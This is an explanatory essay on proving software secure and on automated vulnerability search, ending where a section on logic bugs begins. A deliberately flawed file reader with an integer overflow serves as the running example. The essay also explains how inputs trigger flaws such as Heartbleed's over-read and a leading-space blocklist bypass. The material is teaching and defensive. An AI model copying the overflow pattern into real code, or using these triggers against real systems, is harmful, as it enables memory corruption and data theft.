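# Formal methods for software security, and whether AI-written code and AI models can be verified

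## What does it mean to prove that a program is secure?

Formal methods use mathematical logic to describe what a computer system should do and to reason about whether it does. Researchers began building tools for machine-checked proof in the 1960s, and have since used them on an operating system kernel, a C compiler and cryptographic software. For most programs, a proof would have cost more than the bugs did. In *Prediction*, the computer scientist Kleppmann (2025) expects that to change, because AI models have become good at writing proofs. AI also adds to the demand for verification, because models write code that somebody has to check, and are themselves components of larger systems, with behaviour that nobody wrote down line by line. Whether logic can guarantee anything about AI-written code or the models themselves depends on what such a guarantee consists of.

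A specification is a precise, logical statement of what a program must or must not do. Formal verification means proving by logic that a program, or a model of it, meets a specification for every input the specification covers. Proving that a program is secure therefore requires a specification of what "secure" means for that program. Böhme (2024), in *Fundamental Challenges in Cybersecurity and a Philosophy of Vulnerability-Guided Hardening*, divides security into three demands: an attacker should not be able to read what they should not read, write what they should not write, or disturb the service for others. Someone still has to define what an attacker should not read or write, and what counts as disturbing the service. Whether a flaw is a vulnerability also depends on such definitions, because a vulnerability is a flaw in a system that an attacker can use to break a security requirement.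 The glossary of NIST, the US standards agency, lists more than a dozen official definitions under *vulnerability*, and several of them tie the flaw to a violation of the system's security policy.

People also overlook requirements. In 2018 Google shipped Android 9 with Markup, a tool that let users crop images. Böhme recounts that in 2023 researchers found that the saved file still contained the part the user had cropped out, such as a credit card number. A proof that Markup never crashed would not have ruled out this flaw. In Böhme's account, a proof shows only that certain stated properties hold within a certain model of the system if certain assumptions are met, so nobody proves a program secure outright.

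### A small program with one flaw

Take a program that reads a list of items from a file:

```
read marker (4 bytes); stop unless it equals the fixed value
read n (a 32-bit count)
size = 8 * n              (32-bit arithmetic)
buffer = allocate(size)
for i = 0 to n-1:
    read the next 8-byte item
    write it to the buffer at position 8 * i
```

For a file with three items, the program allocates 24 bytes and fills them. But the multiplication can go wrong, because a 32-bit number can be at most 4,294,967,295. A larger result wraps round, meaning that the machine keeps only the remainder after division by 4,294,967,296. If the file gives n as 536,870,913, then 8 × n is 4,294,967,304, which wraps to 8. The program allocates 8 bytes, enough for one item, and starts writing more than half a billion. A 24-byte file is enough to reach the second write, which overruns the buffer and replaces whatever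 was next to it in memory with bytes that the file's author chose.

MITRE's *CWE-680*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, describes this old pattern, in which a size calculation overflows and the program then overruns a buffer. A related entry, *CWE-190*, quotes code from version 3.3 of the remote-login program OpenSSH in which 1,073,741,824 × 4 wraps to 0. More recently, Beer and Groß (2021), of Google's Project Zero, analyzed spyware used against a Saudi activist's iPhone and found a 32-bit count that wrapped and produced an undersized buffer. The copying loop would have written over 32 gigabytes and crashed the process, but the attackers had arranged memory so that the first few out-of-bounds writes stopped the rest.

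The flaw breaks memory safety, the property that a program never reads or writes memory outside what it has validly allocated. Memory that the program has already freed is no longer validly allocated, so using it is also a violation. Böhme writes that such violations make up most of the largest class of security flaws today.

A repair takes one line: stop if n is greater than 536,870,911.

### Three specifications for the same program

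The weakest useful specification is that the program never writes out of bounds. This means that for every file and every i below n, 8i + 8, calculated without wraparound, must be no greater than size. The file with n = 536,870,913 violates this at i = 1, where 8i + 8 is 16 and size is 8. That file is a counterexample, which is a concrete input or run that violates a specification.

A program that rejects every file never writes out of bounds, so the second specification excludes it by defining the correct result. Given the correct marker and n complete items, the program must return exactly those items in order, and given anything else it must return an error. Whoever writes this specification has to decide something the bounds requirement left open, which is whether the program should reject a genuine file of 536,870,913 items or do its arithmetic in 64 bits and allocate four gigabytes.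 Both options can be safe, but users want only one of them.

The third specification is that the program leaks no secret. Suppose it runs inside a server that also holds an encryption key, and sends its result back to whoever supplied the file. Then what the sender can observe must not depend on the key. Barthe (2026), in *Formalization of Security*, treats this as an instance of noninterference, a policy that Goguen and Meseguer introduced. Unlike the other two specifications, noninterference is a hyperproperty, meaning a property that compares runs. One bad run is enough to show that a program goes out of bounds, but showing that it violates noninterference takes two runs, with the same file and different keys, that look different to the sender.

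Engineers often prove a simple design correct and then show that the real program only does things the design allows, a relation called refinement. But Barthe points out that the usual notion of refinement does not preserve security properties. For example, if the design allows any value in the spare bytes at the end of a reply, a program that puts the key there is a faithful refinement of the design, yet it reveals the key. A security proof also depends on which attacker observations are included in the specification. If only the reply is included, a program whose running time varies with the key still passes.

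The requirements in this list get stronger only if each one is added to those before it. "Leaks no secret" is easy to meet by itself, because a program that sends nothing meets it.

### Finding no flaw and proving there is none

Dijkstra (1970) wrote in *Notes on Structured Programming* that testing can show that bugs are present but never that they are absent. His example was a circuit that multiplied two 27-bit numbers. It had 2⁵⁴ possible inputs, and at some tens of microseconds each, trying them all would have taken more than 10,000 years. Small cases are an exception, since a test of every possible input is a proof. Faster machines can test slightly larger cases this way. At a billion multiplications a second, Dijkstra's circuit would take about seven months. But the file reader's marker and count together make 64 bits, and trying every combination at the same speed would take about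 585 years, without varying any of the items.

So testers try a sample of the possible inputs. A million real files could run through the flawed file reader without a failure, because real files have small counts. Random bytes are even less likely to expose the flaw, since they match the marker only about once in 4.3 billion attempts. Fuzzing, running a program on very many generated inputs and watching for failures, is a far better way to sample, but it still leaves some inputs untested.

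Researchers disagree about how much reassurance to take from a sample of test inputs that reveals no flaws. *STADS* (2018) uses statistics from ecology to estimate the chance that the next generated input will take a new path through the program. In one campaign, that estimate had fallen to about 2 in 100 million after 100 hours. *An Analysis of How Many Undiscovered Vulnerabilities Remain in Information Systems* (2023) argues that even after 300 hours of fuzzing without a find, it is unclear what to believe about the flaws that remain. Ecologists estimate the number of fish in a lake by catching two samples and counting the overlap. This method is hard to apply to crashes because it is often unclear whether two crashes come from the same flaw, and the samples are not independent. Even a good estimate applies only to inputs drawn the way the fuzzer draws them, whereas an attacker who has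 read the code can deliberately write the right marker and the right count on the first attempt.

A proof covers every value of n at once. In the repaired program, n is at most 536,870,911, so 8 × n is at most 4,294,967,288. That fits in 32 bits, so nothing wraps and size is exactly 8 × n. Item i ends at position 8i + 8. Since i is at most n − 1, that position is at most 8 × n, the end of the buffer, so every write stays inside the buffer. The proof assumes that the allocator either provides the number of bytes requested or stops the program. The flaw in the original code is that n can be larger, so the proof fails there at its first step.

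### Why no tool can settle every case

Rice's theorem, from 1953, shows that for any non-trivial question about what programs do when they run, no tool can answer it correctly for every program. *Static Program Analysis* (Møller and Schwartzbach, 2025) explains why with a program that sets x to 17, runs an arbitrary computation, and then sets x to 18 if the computation finishes. A tool that could always tell whether x stays at 17 could also tell whether any given computation finishes, which Turing proved impossible.

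The theorem concerns a single procedure for all programs. It still allows a proof about one program, such as the repaired file reader, and such a proof can draw on the programmer's reasons for writing the code that way, which people can usually explain. It also allows a tool that sometimes answers "don't know". An analysis is sound if, given its assumptions, it never declares a program free of a flaw that the program contains. A sound analysis may still raise false alarms, which are reports of flaws that cannot occur in any real run. For example, a sound tool that did not track the link between n and size would still warn about the repaired loop. Soundness alone is easy to achieve, because a tool that warns about every program is sound. The hard part is keeping the warnings few enough to read. Møller and Schwartzbach note that people also call a testing tool sound when every error it reports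 is genuine, even if it misses others, so soundness in this sense does not support a claim that flaws are absent.

### What a proof rests on

Two kinds of software do most of the logical reasoning. One is the solver, a program that determines whether any values make a logical formula true and, if so, provides them. Z3 is a widely used solver. For the flawed file reader, the formula would combine four conditions: the marker is right, size is 8 × n after wrapping, i is less than n, and 8i + 8 is greater than size. The values n = 536,870,913 and i = 1 make the formula true, so they are the counterexample. If the formula also requires n to be at most 536,870,911, no values make it true. Solvers can run out of time on hard formulas, which leaves the question unanswered.

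A proof assistant, such as Lean, Rocq or Isabelle, is a tool in which people or AI models write proofs for a machine to check. Most of its code helps construct proofs and does not have to be trusted. A deliberately small part, the proof checker, often called the kernel, accepts or rejects each proof. *Formal verification of the S-two AIR* (2026) explains that if faulty automation produces an invalid proof, the kernel rejects it. However, the kernel itself could have a bug. *The Equational Theories Project* (2025), an account of a large collaboration in Lean, describes the worst case, in which a bug lets through a proof of a false statement, from which every other statement follows. The usual safeguard is to check the proof with a second, independently written checker.

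The checker is one part of the trusted base, which is everything that must be correct for a proven property to hold when the program runs. The trusted base also includes the specification, the model of the machine, and any unverified software or hardware. For the file reader, the unverified parts include the allocator, the processor and, unless someone has verified it, the compiler.

The specification needs the most scrutiny, because no checker can confirm that it is the right one. *ProofStudio* (2026) distinguishes verification, which establishes that a statement follows from its assumptions, from validation, which determines whether the statement captures the intended requirement. The extreme case is a vacuous proof, which is valid but shows nothing useful about the program because its statement is too weak or its assumptions can't all be true. For example, the flawed file reader can be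 proved safe if the proof assumes that the marker both equals and does not equal the fixed value.

Milder cases are easier to overlook. In *Kani*, Delmas, Hassan and colleagues (2026) describe a checker for Rust programs and try it on a function that computes greatest common divisors in Firecracker, software that isolates customers' workloads in Amazon's cloud. The function's loop repeats at most 93 times, so unrolling it 94 times would cover every run, but that check had not finished after an hour. They then supplied a loop invariant, a statement that stays true on every pass through the loop, and verification took 0.54 seconds. However, they proved only that the result is greater than zero, which would also be true of a function that always returned 1. The solver could not automatically prove the more natural property, that the result divides both inputs.

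Unrolling the file reader's loop has the same limit. One or two passes expose the flaw in the original version. The repaired version can loop 536,870,911 times, and no solver can handle that many copies of the loop body, so proving it safe requires an argument that covers all passes at once. The main families of methods therefore differ in what a clean result, one that reports no flaw, establishes.

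| Method family | What a clean result establishes |
|---|---|
| Testing and fuzzing | The program did not visibly fail on the inputs tried. |
| Bug-finding analysis of the code, not sound | The tool recognised no flaw; some may remain. |
| Sound static analysis | No run contains a flaw of the stated kind, given the analysis's assumptions. |
| Bounded model checking (a solver on unrolled loops) | No run violates the specification within the bound. This is a full proof only if the tool also shows that no run goes past the bound. |
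| Verification with contracts and loop invariants | The code meets its written contract for every input that the contract allows. |
| Proof in a proof assistant | The stated theorem follows from its stated assumptions. |

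## How do automated tools search a program for vulnerabilities?

The flaw in the file reader appears only when a file has the right marker and a count large enough to make 8 × n wrap round. Four methods can find it without anyone reading the code. Fuzzing runs the program on one file after another. Symbolic execution and bounded model checking translate the code into formulas for a solver, and abstract interpretation works out the range of values each variable can have. The examples below assume the file reader stops with an error if the file runs out of items.

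### Fuzzing with coverage feedback

To fuzz a library, an engineer first writes a test harness, a small program that feeds an input to one part of the library. For *libFuzzer*, a fuzzer from the open-source LLVM compiler project, the harness is a single function that receives an array of bytes. Here, the function would pass those bytes to the file reader as the contents of a file.

The fuzzer then has to produce files. *REDQUEEN* (Aschermann, Schumilo and colleagues, 2019) describes the design of AFL, which many later fuzzers copied. AFL takes a file from a queue, mutates it and runs the program on the result. At first it makes simple changes, such as flipping each bit in turn. Later it makes several random changes at once or splices two files together.

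Coverage feedback determines which mutated files the fuzzer keeps. The compiler inserts a few instructions at every branch point. *Technical Details*, part of the documentation for AFL's successor AFL++, explains that these instructions record each jump from one point to the next and roughly how often it happens. A file that causes a new jump joins the queue, and the fuzzer discards the others. This lets the fuzzer build up an input in stages. LLVM's manual gives a toy program that crashes only on the text "HI!", which it checks one character at a time. A random three-byte guess would have a 1 in 16,777,216 chance of matching. In the manual's sample run, coverage grew at inputs 144, 157, 1,345 and 1,696, and then the program crashed.

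The file reader's marker is harder to match because the program compares all four bytes in one step. A file with three correct bytes takes the same path as a file with none, so the tool cannot detect partial progress. Each byte has 256 possible values, so random bytes match the marker on average once in 256⁴, or 4,294,967,296, attempts. At a thousand runs a second, a match would take about 50 days on average.

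Starting from a real file avoids the problem because the file already contains the correct marker. Without such a file, an engineer can put the marker in a dictionary, a list of byte sequences for the fuzzer to insert at random positions. The engineer can also use AFL++'s *laf-intel instrumentation*, which splits a 32-bit comparison into four 8-bit ones so that each correct byte counts as new coverage. The fuzzer then needs about 1,024 attempts on average (four times 256), if it guesses in the right place.

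Aschermann and colleagues' technique, comparison feedback, runs the program once and records both sides of every comparison, so it needs no dictionary or guesswork. If the file starts with TEST and the program compares those bytes with DATA, the tool finds TEST in the file, replaces it with DATA and runs the program again to see whether coverage improves. It also tries common encodings, such as reversed byte order. AFL++'s manual, *fuzzing in depth*, describes this technique as usually better than splitting comparisons, as long as the program does not transform the input before comparing it.

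Once the marker is right, the size wraps round for seven out of eight possible counts, which are all those from 536,870,912 upwards. Few of these counts cause an overrun in a short file, because the wrapped size for a random n usually leaves room for millions of items, and the file ends long before the buffer is full. For example, the fuzzer might start from a valid file of three items and flip one high bit of the count, turning 3 into 536,870,915. The size is still 24 bytes, so all three items fit and the program stops at the end of the file. If another mutation adds eight bytes to the file, the fourth write overruns the buffer.

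Even then the program may not crash, since the extra bytes may land in memory that nothing uses again. Fuzzers therefore work with sanitizers, checks that the compiler adds to a program to stop it as soon as a violation occurs. LLVM's *AddressSanitizer* detects out-of-bounds accesses and uses of freed memory. It typically halves the program's speed, and it does not produce false alarms. In the file reader, it would report the fourth write immediately. Other sanitizers detect reads of uninitialised memory or operations that the C language leaves undefined.

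Fuzzing is not sound, but it needs only a harness and computing time, and it works on very large programs. In *From Formal Methods to Fuzzing and Back*, Donaldson (2026) recalls switching to fuzzing after struggling for about twelve years to make formal methods scale, and finding real bugs in projects with millions of lines of code. Fuzzers tend to miss flaws behind conditions that are hard to satisfy by making small changes to the input, such as a checksum over the whole file, because changing any other byte makes the checksum wrong. LLVM's manual suggests fuzzing a special build with such checks switched off. Aschermann and colleagues automate a similar approach, removing the check during the search and repairing the file afterwards.

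### Symbolic and concolic execution

Symbolic execution tries to calculate, rather than guess, which file leads to the flaw. It runs the program with symbols in place of the input. Baldoni, Coppa and colleagues (2016) explain in *A Survey of Symbolic Execution Techniques* that the engine keeps two records for each path: an expression for the value of each variable, and a path condition, a formula that an input must satisfy to follow that path. At a branch, the engine splits the path in two and adds the branch's condition to one copy's path condition and its opposite to the other's.

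In the file reader, the first branch adds the condition that the marker equals the fixed value, M. The multiplication sets size to the remainder of 8 × n. Entering the loop a second time requires n to be greater than 1. The engine then asks the solver whether the second write can go out of bounds, which means asking whether all of these statements can be true together:

```
marker = M
n > 1
size = (8 × n) mod 4,294,967,296
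16 > size
```

Only fourteen counts satisfy the formula, including the one from the original example, n = 536,870,913. A random 24-byte file has about one chance in 1.3 × 10¹⁸ of containing the marker and one of those counts, but a solver can easily find values that work.

Concolic execution, a blend of "concrete" and "symbolic", explores a program's paths through a series of ordinary runs. Suppose the first file is all zeros. The run fails at the marker check, so its path condition is marker ≠ M. The engine negates this condition and uses the solver to find a matching input, say a file with the right marker and a count of zero. That run skips the loop, which adds the condition n ≤ 0. Negating that new condition gives a file with at least one item, and so on. At each write, the engine can also use the solver to look for values that would put the write out of bounds.

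Because every run is real, the engine can observe which branch the program takes, and the solver has less to do. The program can also call code that the engine cannot translate, such as a closed-source library, but the engine then has no formula linking that code's inputs to its outputs. In an example from Baldoni and colleagues, a function branches on a value returned by such code, and the engine may never generate an input that takes the other branch. Sometimes a generated input also takes a different path from the one the engine predicted, and they cite a study that reported rates of over 60%.

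A more basic difficulty is path explosion. Every branch can double the number of paths, and a loop adds a new branch on every pass. The repaired file reader has a separate path for each count from 0 to 536,870,911, even if every file is complete. If the loop also skipped any item equal to zero, each item would double the number of paths, and there would be about 1.1 trillion paths for a file of 40 items.

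Engines can reduce the number of paths by stopping a loop after a few passes or by fixing the value of part of the input, such as the marker, in advance. They can also merge two paths that rejoin, replacing them with a single expression such as "if the item is zero, this value, otherwise that one", but this gives the solver harder formulas. *Symbolic Execution in Practice* (2025) identifies solving as the main bottleneck and finds that such techniques make larger programs feasible to analyze but don't eliminate path explosion.

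In principle, symbolic execution can be sound and free of false alarms if the engine explores every path and the solver answers every query. On most real programs, the engine stops long before it has explored every path, so a clean result does not rule out flaws on the paths it did not reach. The flaws it misses tend to be deep inside loops, behind arithmetic that the solver cannot handle, or in code that the engine does not track.

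### Bounded model checking

Bounded model checking puts many paths into one formula. The tool replaces each loop with k copies of its body and translates the result into a formula that is true exactly when some run within those k passes violates the specification. For the file reader with k = 2, and a file long enough for two items, the formula is:

```
marker = M
and size = (8 × n) mod 4,294,967,296
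and ( (n > 0 and 8 > size)  or  (n > 1 and 16 > size) )
```

A third pass would add "or (n > 2 and 24 > size)", but one pass is enough to find the flaw, because n = 536,870,912 gives a size of zero, so the first write overruns. *CBMC* (Kroening, Schrammel and Tautschnig, 2023) describes a checker for C programs that turns such a solution into a trace, a list of the steps leading to the violation with the value of each variable.

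Some flaws appear only after many passes through the loop. Suppose the programmer had instead allocated a fixed 8,000 bytes, whatever the count. That is room for 1,000 items, so the first bad write happens on pass 1,001, and a check with k = 1,000 or less would miss it. Kroening and colleagues show the same effect in a small program that manages a lock, where CBMC finds a violation at a bound of two but not at a bound of one.

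To check whether the bound was large enough, CBMC can add an unwinding assertion, which fails if any run could continue past the last copy of the loop. In Kroening and colleagues' example of a binary search through 16 elements, the assertion holds at six passes, so the clean result covers every run. For the repaired file reader with k = 10, the assertion fails, and a file with n = 11 is a counterexample. In the same situation, another checker, CPAchecker, returns UNKNOWN, according to *Software Verification with CPAchecker 3.0* (2024).

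An engineer could remove the failure by telling the tool to assume that n is at most 10, but the original program would then pass too, because the assumption excludes every count that wraps round. For the repaired program, the proof would be valid for files of up to ten items.

The value of a bounded check that finds no flaws depends partly on how often flaws appear only in large cases. Donaldson uses a tool that relies on the small scope hypothesis, the idea that most defects appear in some small example. In Donaldson's work on the specifications of two languages for graphics processors, all the problems appeared in modest examples, and after the team fixed them, a search of much larger examples found no more. This is a good reason to use bounded checking to find bugs, but it is weaker evidence that a program is safe from attackers, who can use large cases.

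A higher bound makes the formula larger and the check slower. A loop of 100 passes inside another loop of 100 passes produces 10,000 copies of the inner body. *Verifying components of Arm(R) Confidential Computing Architecture with ESBMC* (2024) reports that setting a separate bound for each loop can keep the formula smaller and the check faster. Solver running times are also unpredictable. Donaldson's earlier tool GPUVerify, which checked programs for graphics processors, ran quickly on some programs and very slowly on others, and an optimisation that simplified a program could make the check slower.

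Bounded model checking is sound only when the bound covers every run. The usual obstacle is a loop like the file reader's, where the number of iterations depends on the input. *Model Checking C Programs with Loops via k-Induction and Invariants* (2015) proposes to handle such loops by having the tool attempt a proof by induction, without a loop invariant from the programmer.

### Static analysis by abstract interpretation

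Abstract interpretation covers all passes of a loop by giving up detail. The analyzer tracks a simplified description of all the values a variable could have, rather than the exact values. The simplest useful description is an interval. *A Review of Formal Methods applied to Machine Learning* (2021) traces the theory to work by Cousot and Cousot in the late 1970s.

The original file reader doesn't restrict the count, so n can be any 32-bit number. The analyzer multiplies both ends of the interval by 8 and compares the result with the 32-bit limit.

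| | Original program | With n at most 536,870,911 |
|---|---|---|
| Interval for n | 0 to 4,294,967,295 | 0 to 536,870,911 |
| Interval for 8 × n, before wrapping | 0 to 34,359,738,360 | 0 to 4,294,967,288 |
| Result for the multiplication | Alarm: it may wrap | No alarm |

The analyzer has covered every possible count without running the program. It handles the loop similarly. The variable i starts at 0, and after one pass its interval is 0 to 1, then 0 to 2. Growing the interval one step at a time would take over 500 million steps, so analyzers use widening, which jumps to a much larger interval, such as every value i can hold. The loop's condition, that i is less than n, then narrows this to 0 to 536,870,910.

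However, the analyzer still raises a false alarm at the write in the repaired program. It has to show that 8i + 8 is never greater than size. Its intervals for both extend up to 4,294,967,288, and they allow combinations such as size = 40 and i = 100, where the write would end at byte 808. No real run can do this, because a size of 40 means that n is 5 and i is at most 4. The alarm occurs because separate intervals do not record this connection between size and i.

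An analyzer that also tracks relations between variables, such as size = 8 × n and i ≤ n − 1, can prove the write safe, but it needs more computation. Choosing what to track is much of the work. In *A Static Analyzer for Large Safety-Critical Software*, Blanchet, Cousot and colleagues report few or no false alarms on a family of large control programs. They achieved this by refining a general analyzer with several more precise descriptions of values, which its users then adapted to their programs.

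Other simplifications have the same weakness. To handle thousands of parallel threads, GPUVerify examined two at a time and treated whatever the others wrote to shared memory as unknown. Donaldson considers this a good trade-off for most programs, but it caused false alarms when safety depended on a value that another thread had written.

Abstract interpretation is sound by design, so an interval may be too wide but never leaves out a value that can occur. *A Review of Formal Methods applied to Machine Learning* notes that researchers usually prove this soundness on paper, so the proof may contain errors and the analyzer itself may have bugs. The main drawback is the time people spend on false alarms, which many tools avoid by giving up soundness. *Towards security defect prediction with AI* (2018) contrasts a sound analysis in the tool Frama-C with the Clang static analyzer, which by default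 cuts loops short to limit the number of cases. Even a sound analyzer does not detect flaws outside the class it checks. For example, intervals can show that a write stays inside a buffer, but they contain no information about who is allowed to read the result.

### Why every method needs a failure signal

Suppose the file reader runs on a server that stores files for many users, and the programmer forgot to check that the requester owns the file. An attacker requests another user's file. The marker is correct, the count is small, every write stays inside the buffer, and the program returns the items in order and exits normally. A fuzzer may produce this request thousands of times and discard it each time.

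Solvers also need a description of the flaw, which in the formulas above is 16 > size. Without it, the solver can still produce files that reach the second write, but it cannot identify which of them trigger the flaw. Kroening and colleagues demonstrate this with a short function that calculates absolute values. CBMC first reported that verification was successful because the code contained no assertions to check. When they switched on the check for arithmetic overflow, CBMC found that the function fails on −2,147,483,648, the one negative 32-bit number with no positive counterpart.

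Memory errors are easier to search for automatically because the rule against them is the same in every program. Wang, Görz and colleagues (2025) observe in *Anota* that a memory violation is never correct, whereas someone has to specify how an application's own logic should behave. They classify 27 of the 40 most dangerous software weaknesses on MITRE's list as flaws in application logic. One of their examples is a Python program that refuses to fetch web addresses on a blocklist. Python's address parser mishandled addresses that begin with a space, so adding a space before a blocked address got it past the filter. A fuzzer could easily try that input, but the program would fetch the page without crashing or breaking any rule that existing sanitizers check.

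Hard-coded passwords raise the same problem. *ROSA* (2025) points out that comparison feedback can help a fuzzer get past the check for such a password, just as it does with a marker. But a successful login is not a crash, so the fuzzer also needs a way to detect that this login should have failed.

One way to detect a bug is to compare runs that should give the same result. *SoK* (2026), a review of browser security, notes that memory sanitizers cannot detect logic bugs, and lists fuzzers that run the same script at different levels of optimisation and look for differences. Donaldson's GraphicsFuzz tested the compilers in graphics drivers, which have no single correct output image. It rewrote a graphics program in ways that should not change its meaning, ran both versions on the same device and reported a bug if the images differed noticeably.

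Databases can be tested with a simple comparison. For any condition, such as "the price is above 5", each row either satisfies it, fails it or has no price. Three queries, one for each case, should together return exactly the rows in the table. If they do not, the tester has found a bug in the database without needing to know which rows each query should have returned. Donaldson calls such rules partial specifications because they state something that must be true of the output without defining it completely.

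Comparison does not help find the missing ownership check, since the server would hand over the file every time. Someone has to specify who may read what. Wang and colleagues let developers do this with short annotations in the code, which can state, for example, that only administrators may run a certain function. A monitor checks these policies while the program runs and reports violations as crashes, which an ordinary fuzzer can detect. But if a developer forgets both the ownership check and the annotation, the fuzzer still misses the flaw.

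## What has automated search found, and what has it missed?

Symbolic execution produced some of the first large-scale results. *KLEE* (Cadar, Dunbar and Engler, 2008) reported running a tool of the same name on all 89 stand-alone programs in GNU Coreutils, the basic commands that millions of Unix systems use for jobs such as copying and sorting files. Given about an hour per program, the tool generated tests that covered over 90% of the lines on average, more than the tests developers had written by hand over 15 years. Across 452 programs it found 56 serious bugs, including three in Coreutils that people had missed for more than 15 years. The programs were small, though, and together had only about 430,000 lines.

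Microsoft's SAGE applied concolic execution to larger programs, the parts of Windows that read images, documents and other files. Its builders, Godefroid, Levin and Molnar, tried it on a flaw in animated cursors that had forced Microsoft to issue an emergency patch in 2007. Triggering the flaw required a file with two header records. Ordinary cursor files have one, so small mutations of them had not exposed it. Starting from an ordinary file, SAGE produced one that caused a crash after 7,706 attempts, in 7 hours and 36 minutes. The team later reported that SAGE had found about a third of the bugs that file fuzzing uncovered during the development of Windows 7. Microsoft usually ran SAGE last, so the other tools had already missed those bugs.

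### Heartbleed

In April 2014 the public learned of a flaw in OpenSSL, the library that encrypted traffic for a large share of the world's websites. To check that a connection was alive, a client could send the server a short "heartbeat" message, which the server would send back. The message included a two-byte field giving its length, and OpenSSL copied the stated number of bytes into the reply without checking that the message was that long. An attacker could send one byte, state a length of 65,535, and receive up to 64 kilobytes of whatever lay next to the message in memory, sometimes including passwords or private keys. Released versions had contained the flaw since March 2012.

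A fuzzer could have triggered Heartbleed without anyone noticing. The server read past the end of a buffer but wrote nothing out of place, so it usually kept running and sent a normal-looking reply. OpenSSL also reused its own buffers, which made over-reads harder for memory checkers to detect.

Static analyzers failed for a different reason. To report the copy as dangerous, a tool had to trace the length back to the network. Andy Chou, a co-founder of the code-analysis company Coverity, explained that its analyzer had failed to do this. Programs often swap the byte order of numbers that arrive over a network, so the company then tried having the analyzer treat any byte-swapped number as untrusted. With that rule, the analyzer flagged Heartbleed.

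A year after Heartbleed was disclosed in April 2014, the journalist Hanno Böck fuzzed a vulnerable version of OpenSSL with AFL and AddressSanitizer and found the flaw within six hours. Both tools had existed before the disclosure.

### Flaws that survive continuous fuzzing

Google started OSS-Fuzz in December 2016, partly in response to Heartbleed. It continuously fuzzes important open-source projects on Google's machines. By May 2025 it had helped find and fix more than 13,000 vulnerabilities and 50,000 bugs across 1,000 projects.

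Many flaws survive because no harness reaches them. In 2023 Google estimated that its fuzzers covered about 30% of a typical project's code. When it later used language models to write more harnesses, it found 26 new vulnerabilities, including one in OpenSSL that had probably been there for two decades.

Other flaws remain in code that fuzzers run constantly. Anthropic (2026) describes a 16-year-old flaw in FFmpeg, a video library, on a line that automated tests had run five million times. Tests can run a line many times and still miss a flaw that only a rare value triggers, like the one in the file reader.

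### Contests with planted flaws

DARPA, the US defence research agency, has twice run contests for systems that find and patch flaws with no human help. In the Cyber Grand Challenge of August 2016, seven machines attacked and defended programs written for the event. The programs ran on an operating system with only seven system calls, so the contest avoided much of what makes real software hard to analyze. The winner, Mayhem, combined fuzzing with symbolic execution. It then finished last against human teams in the tournament at the hacker conference DEF CON.

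The AI Cyber Challenge used real open-source projects and let the teams use language models. The organisers planted flaws in the code so they could count what the systems missed, which is impossible in an ordinary search. DARPA (2024) reported that in the semifinal the systems found 22 planted flaws, patched 15 of them and found one real flaw in the database SQLite. In the August 2025 final, seven systems ran on their own for about 143 hours, according to a second paper titled *SoK*, a study of the contest.

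Together the finalists found 54 planted flaws and patched 43. *Challenge showcases AI's power to secure America's health care*, from partner agency ARPA-H, counts 63 challenges, which gives the widely quoted rates of 86% found and 68% patched. DARPA's *AIxCC Main Stage Presentation* counts 70 known vulnerabilities, which gives 77% and 61%. The systems also found 18 real flaws, six in C code and 12 in Java, and produced 11 patches, all for the Java flaws.

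DARPA put the average cost at about $152 per task. A task could be demonstrating a flaw, patching it or assessing a report, and several teams could complete the same one. Computing and language models cost $359,000 in total, or about $5,000 for each of the 72 distinct flaws. That is still modest, because companies sometimes pay outside researchers hundreds of thousands of dollars for one bug. After the final, DARPA paid the teams to try their systems on other important software, and by March 2026 they had found 83 more vulnerabilities there, Cybersecurity Dive reported.

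### Language models on real software

Google's Big Sleep, an agent built around a language model, found an exploitable flaw in SQLite in October 2024. SQLite uses −1 in place of a column number to refer to a row's built-in ID. One function did not handle that case and wrote just before the start of a buffer. The OSS-Fuzz harness left out the extension that contained this function, but Google's researchers still did not find the flaw when they fuzzed the right code for 150 CPU-hours. Big Sleep had started from recent changes to the code and looked for related mistakes. In August 2025 Google announced a first batch of 20 vulnerabilities that Big Sleep had found.

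Models then improved quickly. Anthropic's *Launching an opt-in vulnerability-finding service for open-source software* (2026) reports that success rates on CyberGym, a benchmark of vulnerability finding, rose from under 20% at the start of 2025 to over 85% in 2026. In April 2026 Anthropic announced a model called Claude Mythos Preview but withheld it from general release. At the same time it announced Project Glasswing, which gave selected organisations access to the model so that they could fix their software first.

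Anthropic's *Project Glasswing* (2026) reports that about 50 partners had found more than 10,000 high- or critical-severity vulnerabilities by late May. *Anthropic's New AI Model Can Identify More Software Bugs Than Ever* (Dudley and Burke, 2026) describes a presentation from Microsoft, one of the partners, showing that Mythos had uncovered 90 critical and 141 important bugs in SharePoint, the company's collaboration software, in April alone.

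Anthropic also scanned open-source projects itself. The table combines its May update with figures copied from its website in Coopersmith's *Anthropic's coordinated vulnerability disclosure dashboard* (2026). The November figures come from two EconoTimes articles, *Anthropic Dashboard Lists 37,966 Vulnerability Candidates, 6,009 Confirmed Valid* (2026) and *Anthropic Says It Fixed More Than 18,000 Internal Security Issues* (2026). A candidate is any distinct crash or suspected flaw that the model reports, before anyone checks it.

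| Open-source scan | May 2026 | November 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Candidates | 23,019 | 37,966 |
| Candidates that reviewers checked | 1,752 (only those the model rated high or critical) | 6,376 |
| Valid, among those checked | 1,587 (90.6%) | 6,009 (94.2%) |
| Reported to maintainers | 1,596 in 281 projects | 5,087 in 680 projects |
| Confirmed patched | 97 | 629 |

### Firefox

The most detailed outside account is Mozilla's *Behind the Scenes Hardening Firefox with Claude Mythos Preview* (2026). Mozilla fixed 423 security bugs in Firefox in April 2026, compared with 20 to 30 in a typical month of 2025. Mythos Preview had identified 271 of the 423, all fixed in Firefox 150. Mozilla rated 180 of those 271 as high severity, 80 as moderate and 11 as low.

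Mozilla's engineers had asked earlier models, such as GPT-4, to read risky code, but the models raised too many false alarms. The newer system gives the model a file, tells it that the file contains a bug, and asks for a test case that triggers it. The system then runs the test to filter out suspected bugs that the model cannot reproduce.

Some of the bugs were 15 or 20 years old. In one, which resembles the flaw in the file reader, an HTML table with more than 65,535 rows overflowed a 16-bit field in the layout code. Fuzzers had missed this bug for years, even though the test case is tiny. Many others were at the boundary between the sandboxed process that displays a web page and the privileged process that controls the browser. Mozilla describes this boundary as very hard to fuzz.

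In the logs, the model also repeatedly tried and failed to escape the sandbox by altering prototypes, the shared templates from which JavaScript objects inherit. Researchers had reported several such escapes in earlier years, and Mozilla had responded by freezing the prototypes rather than fixing each case.

### Logic bugs

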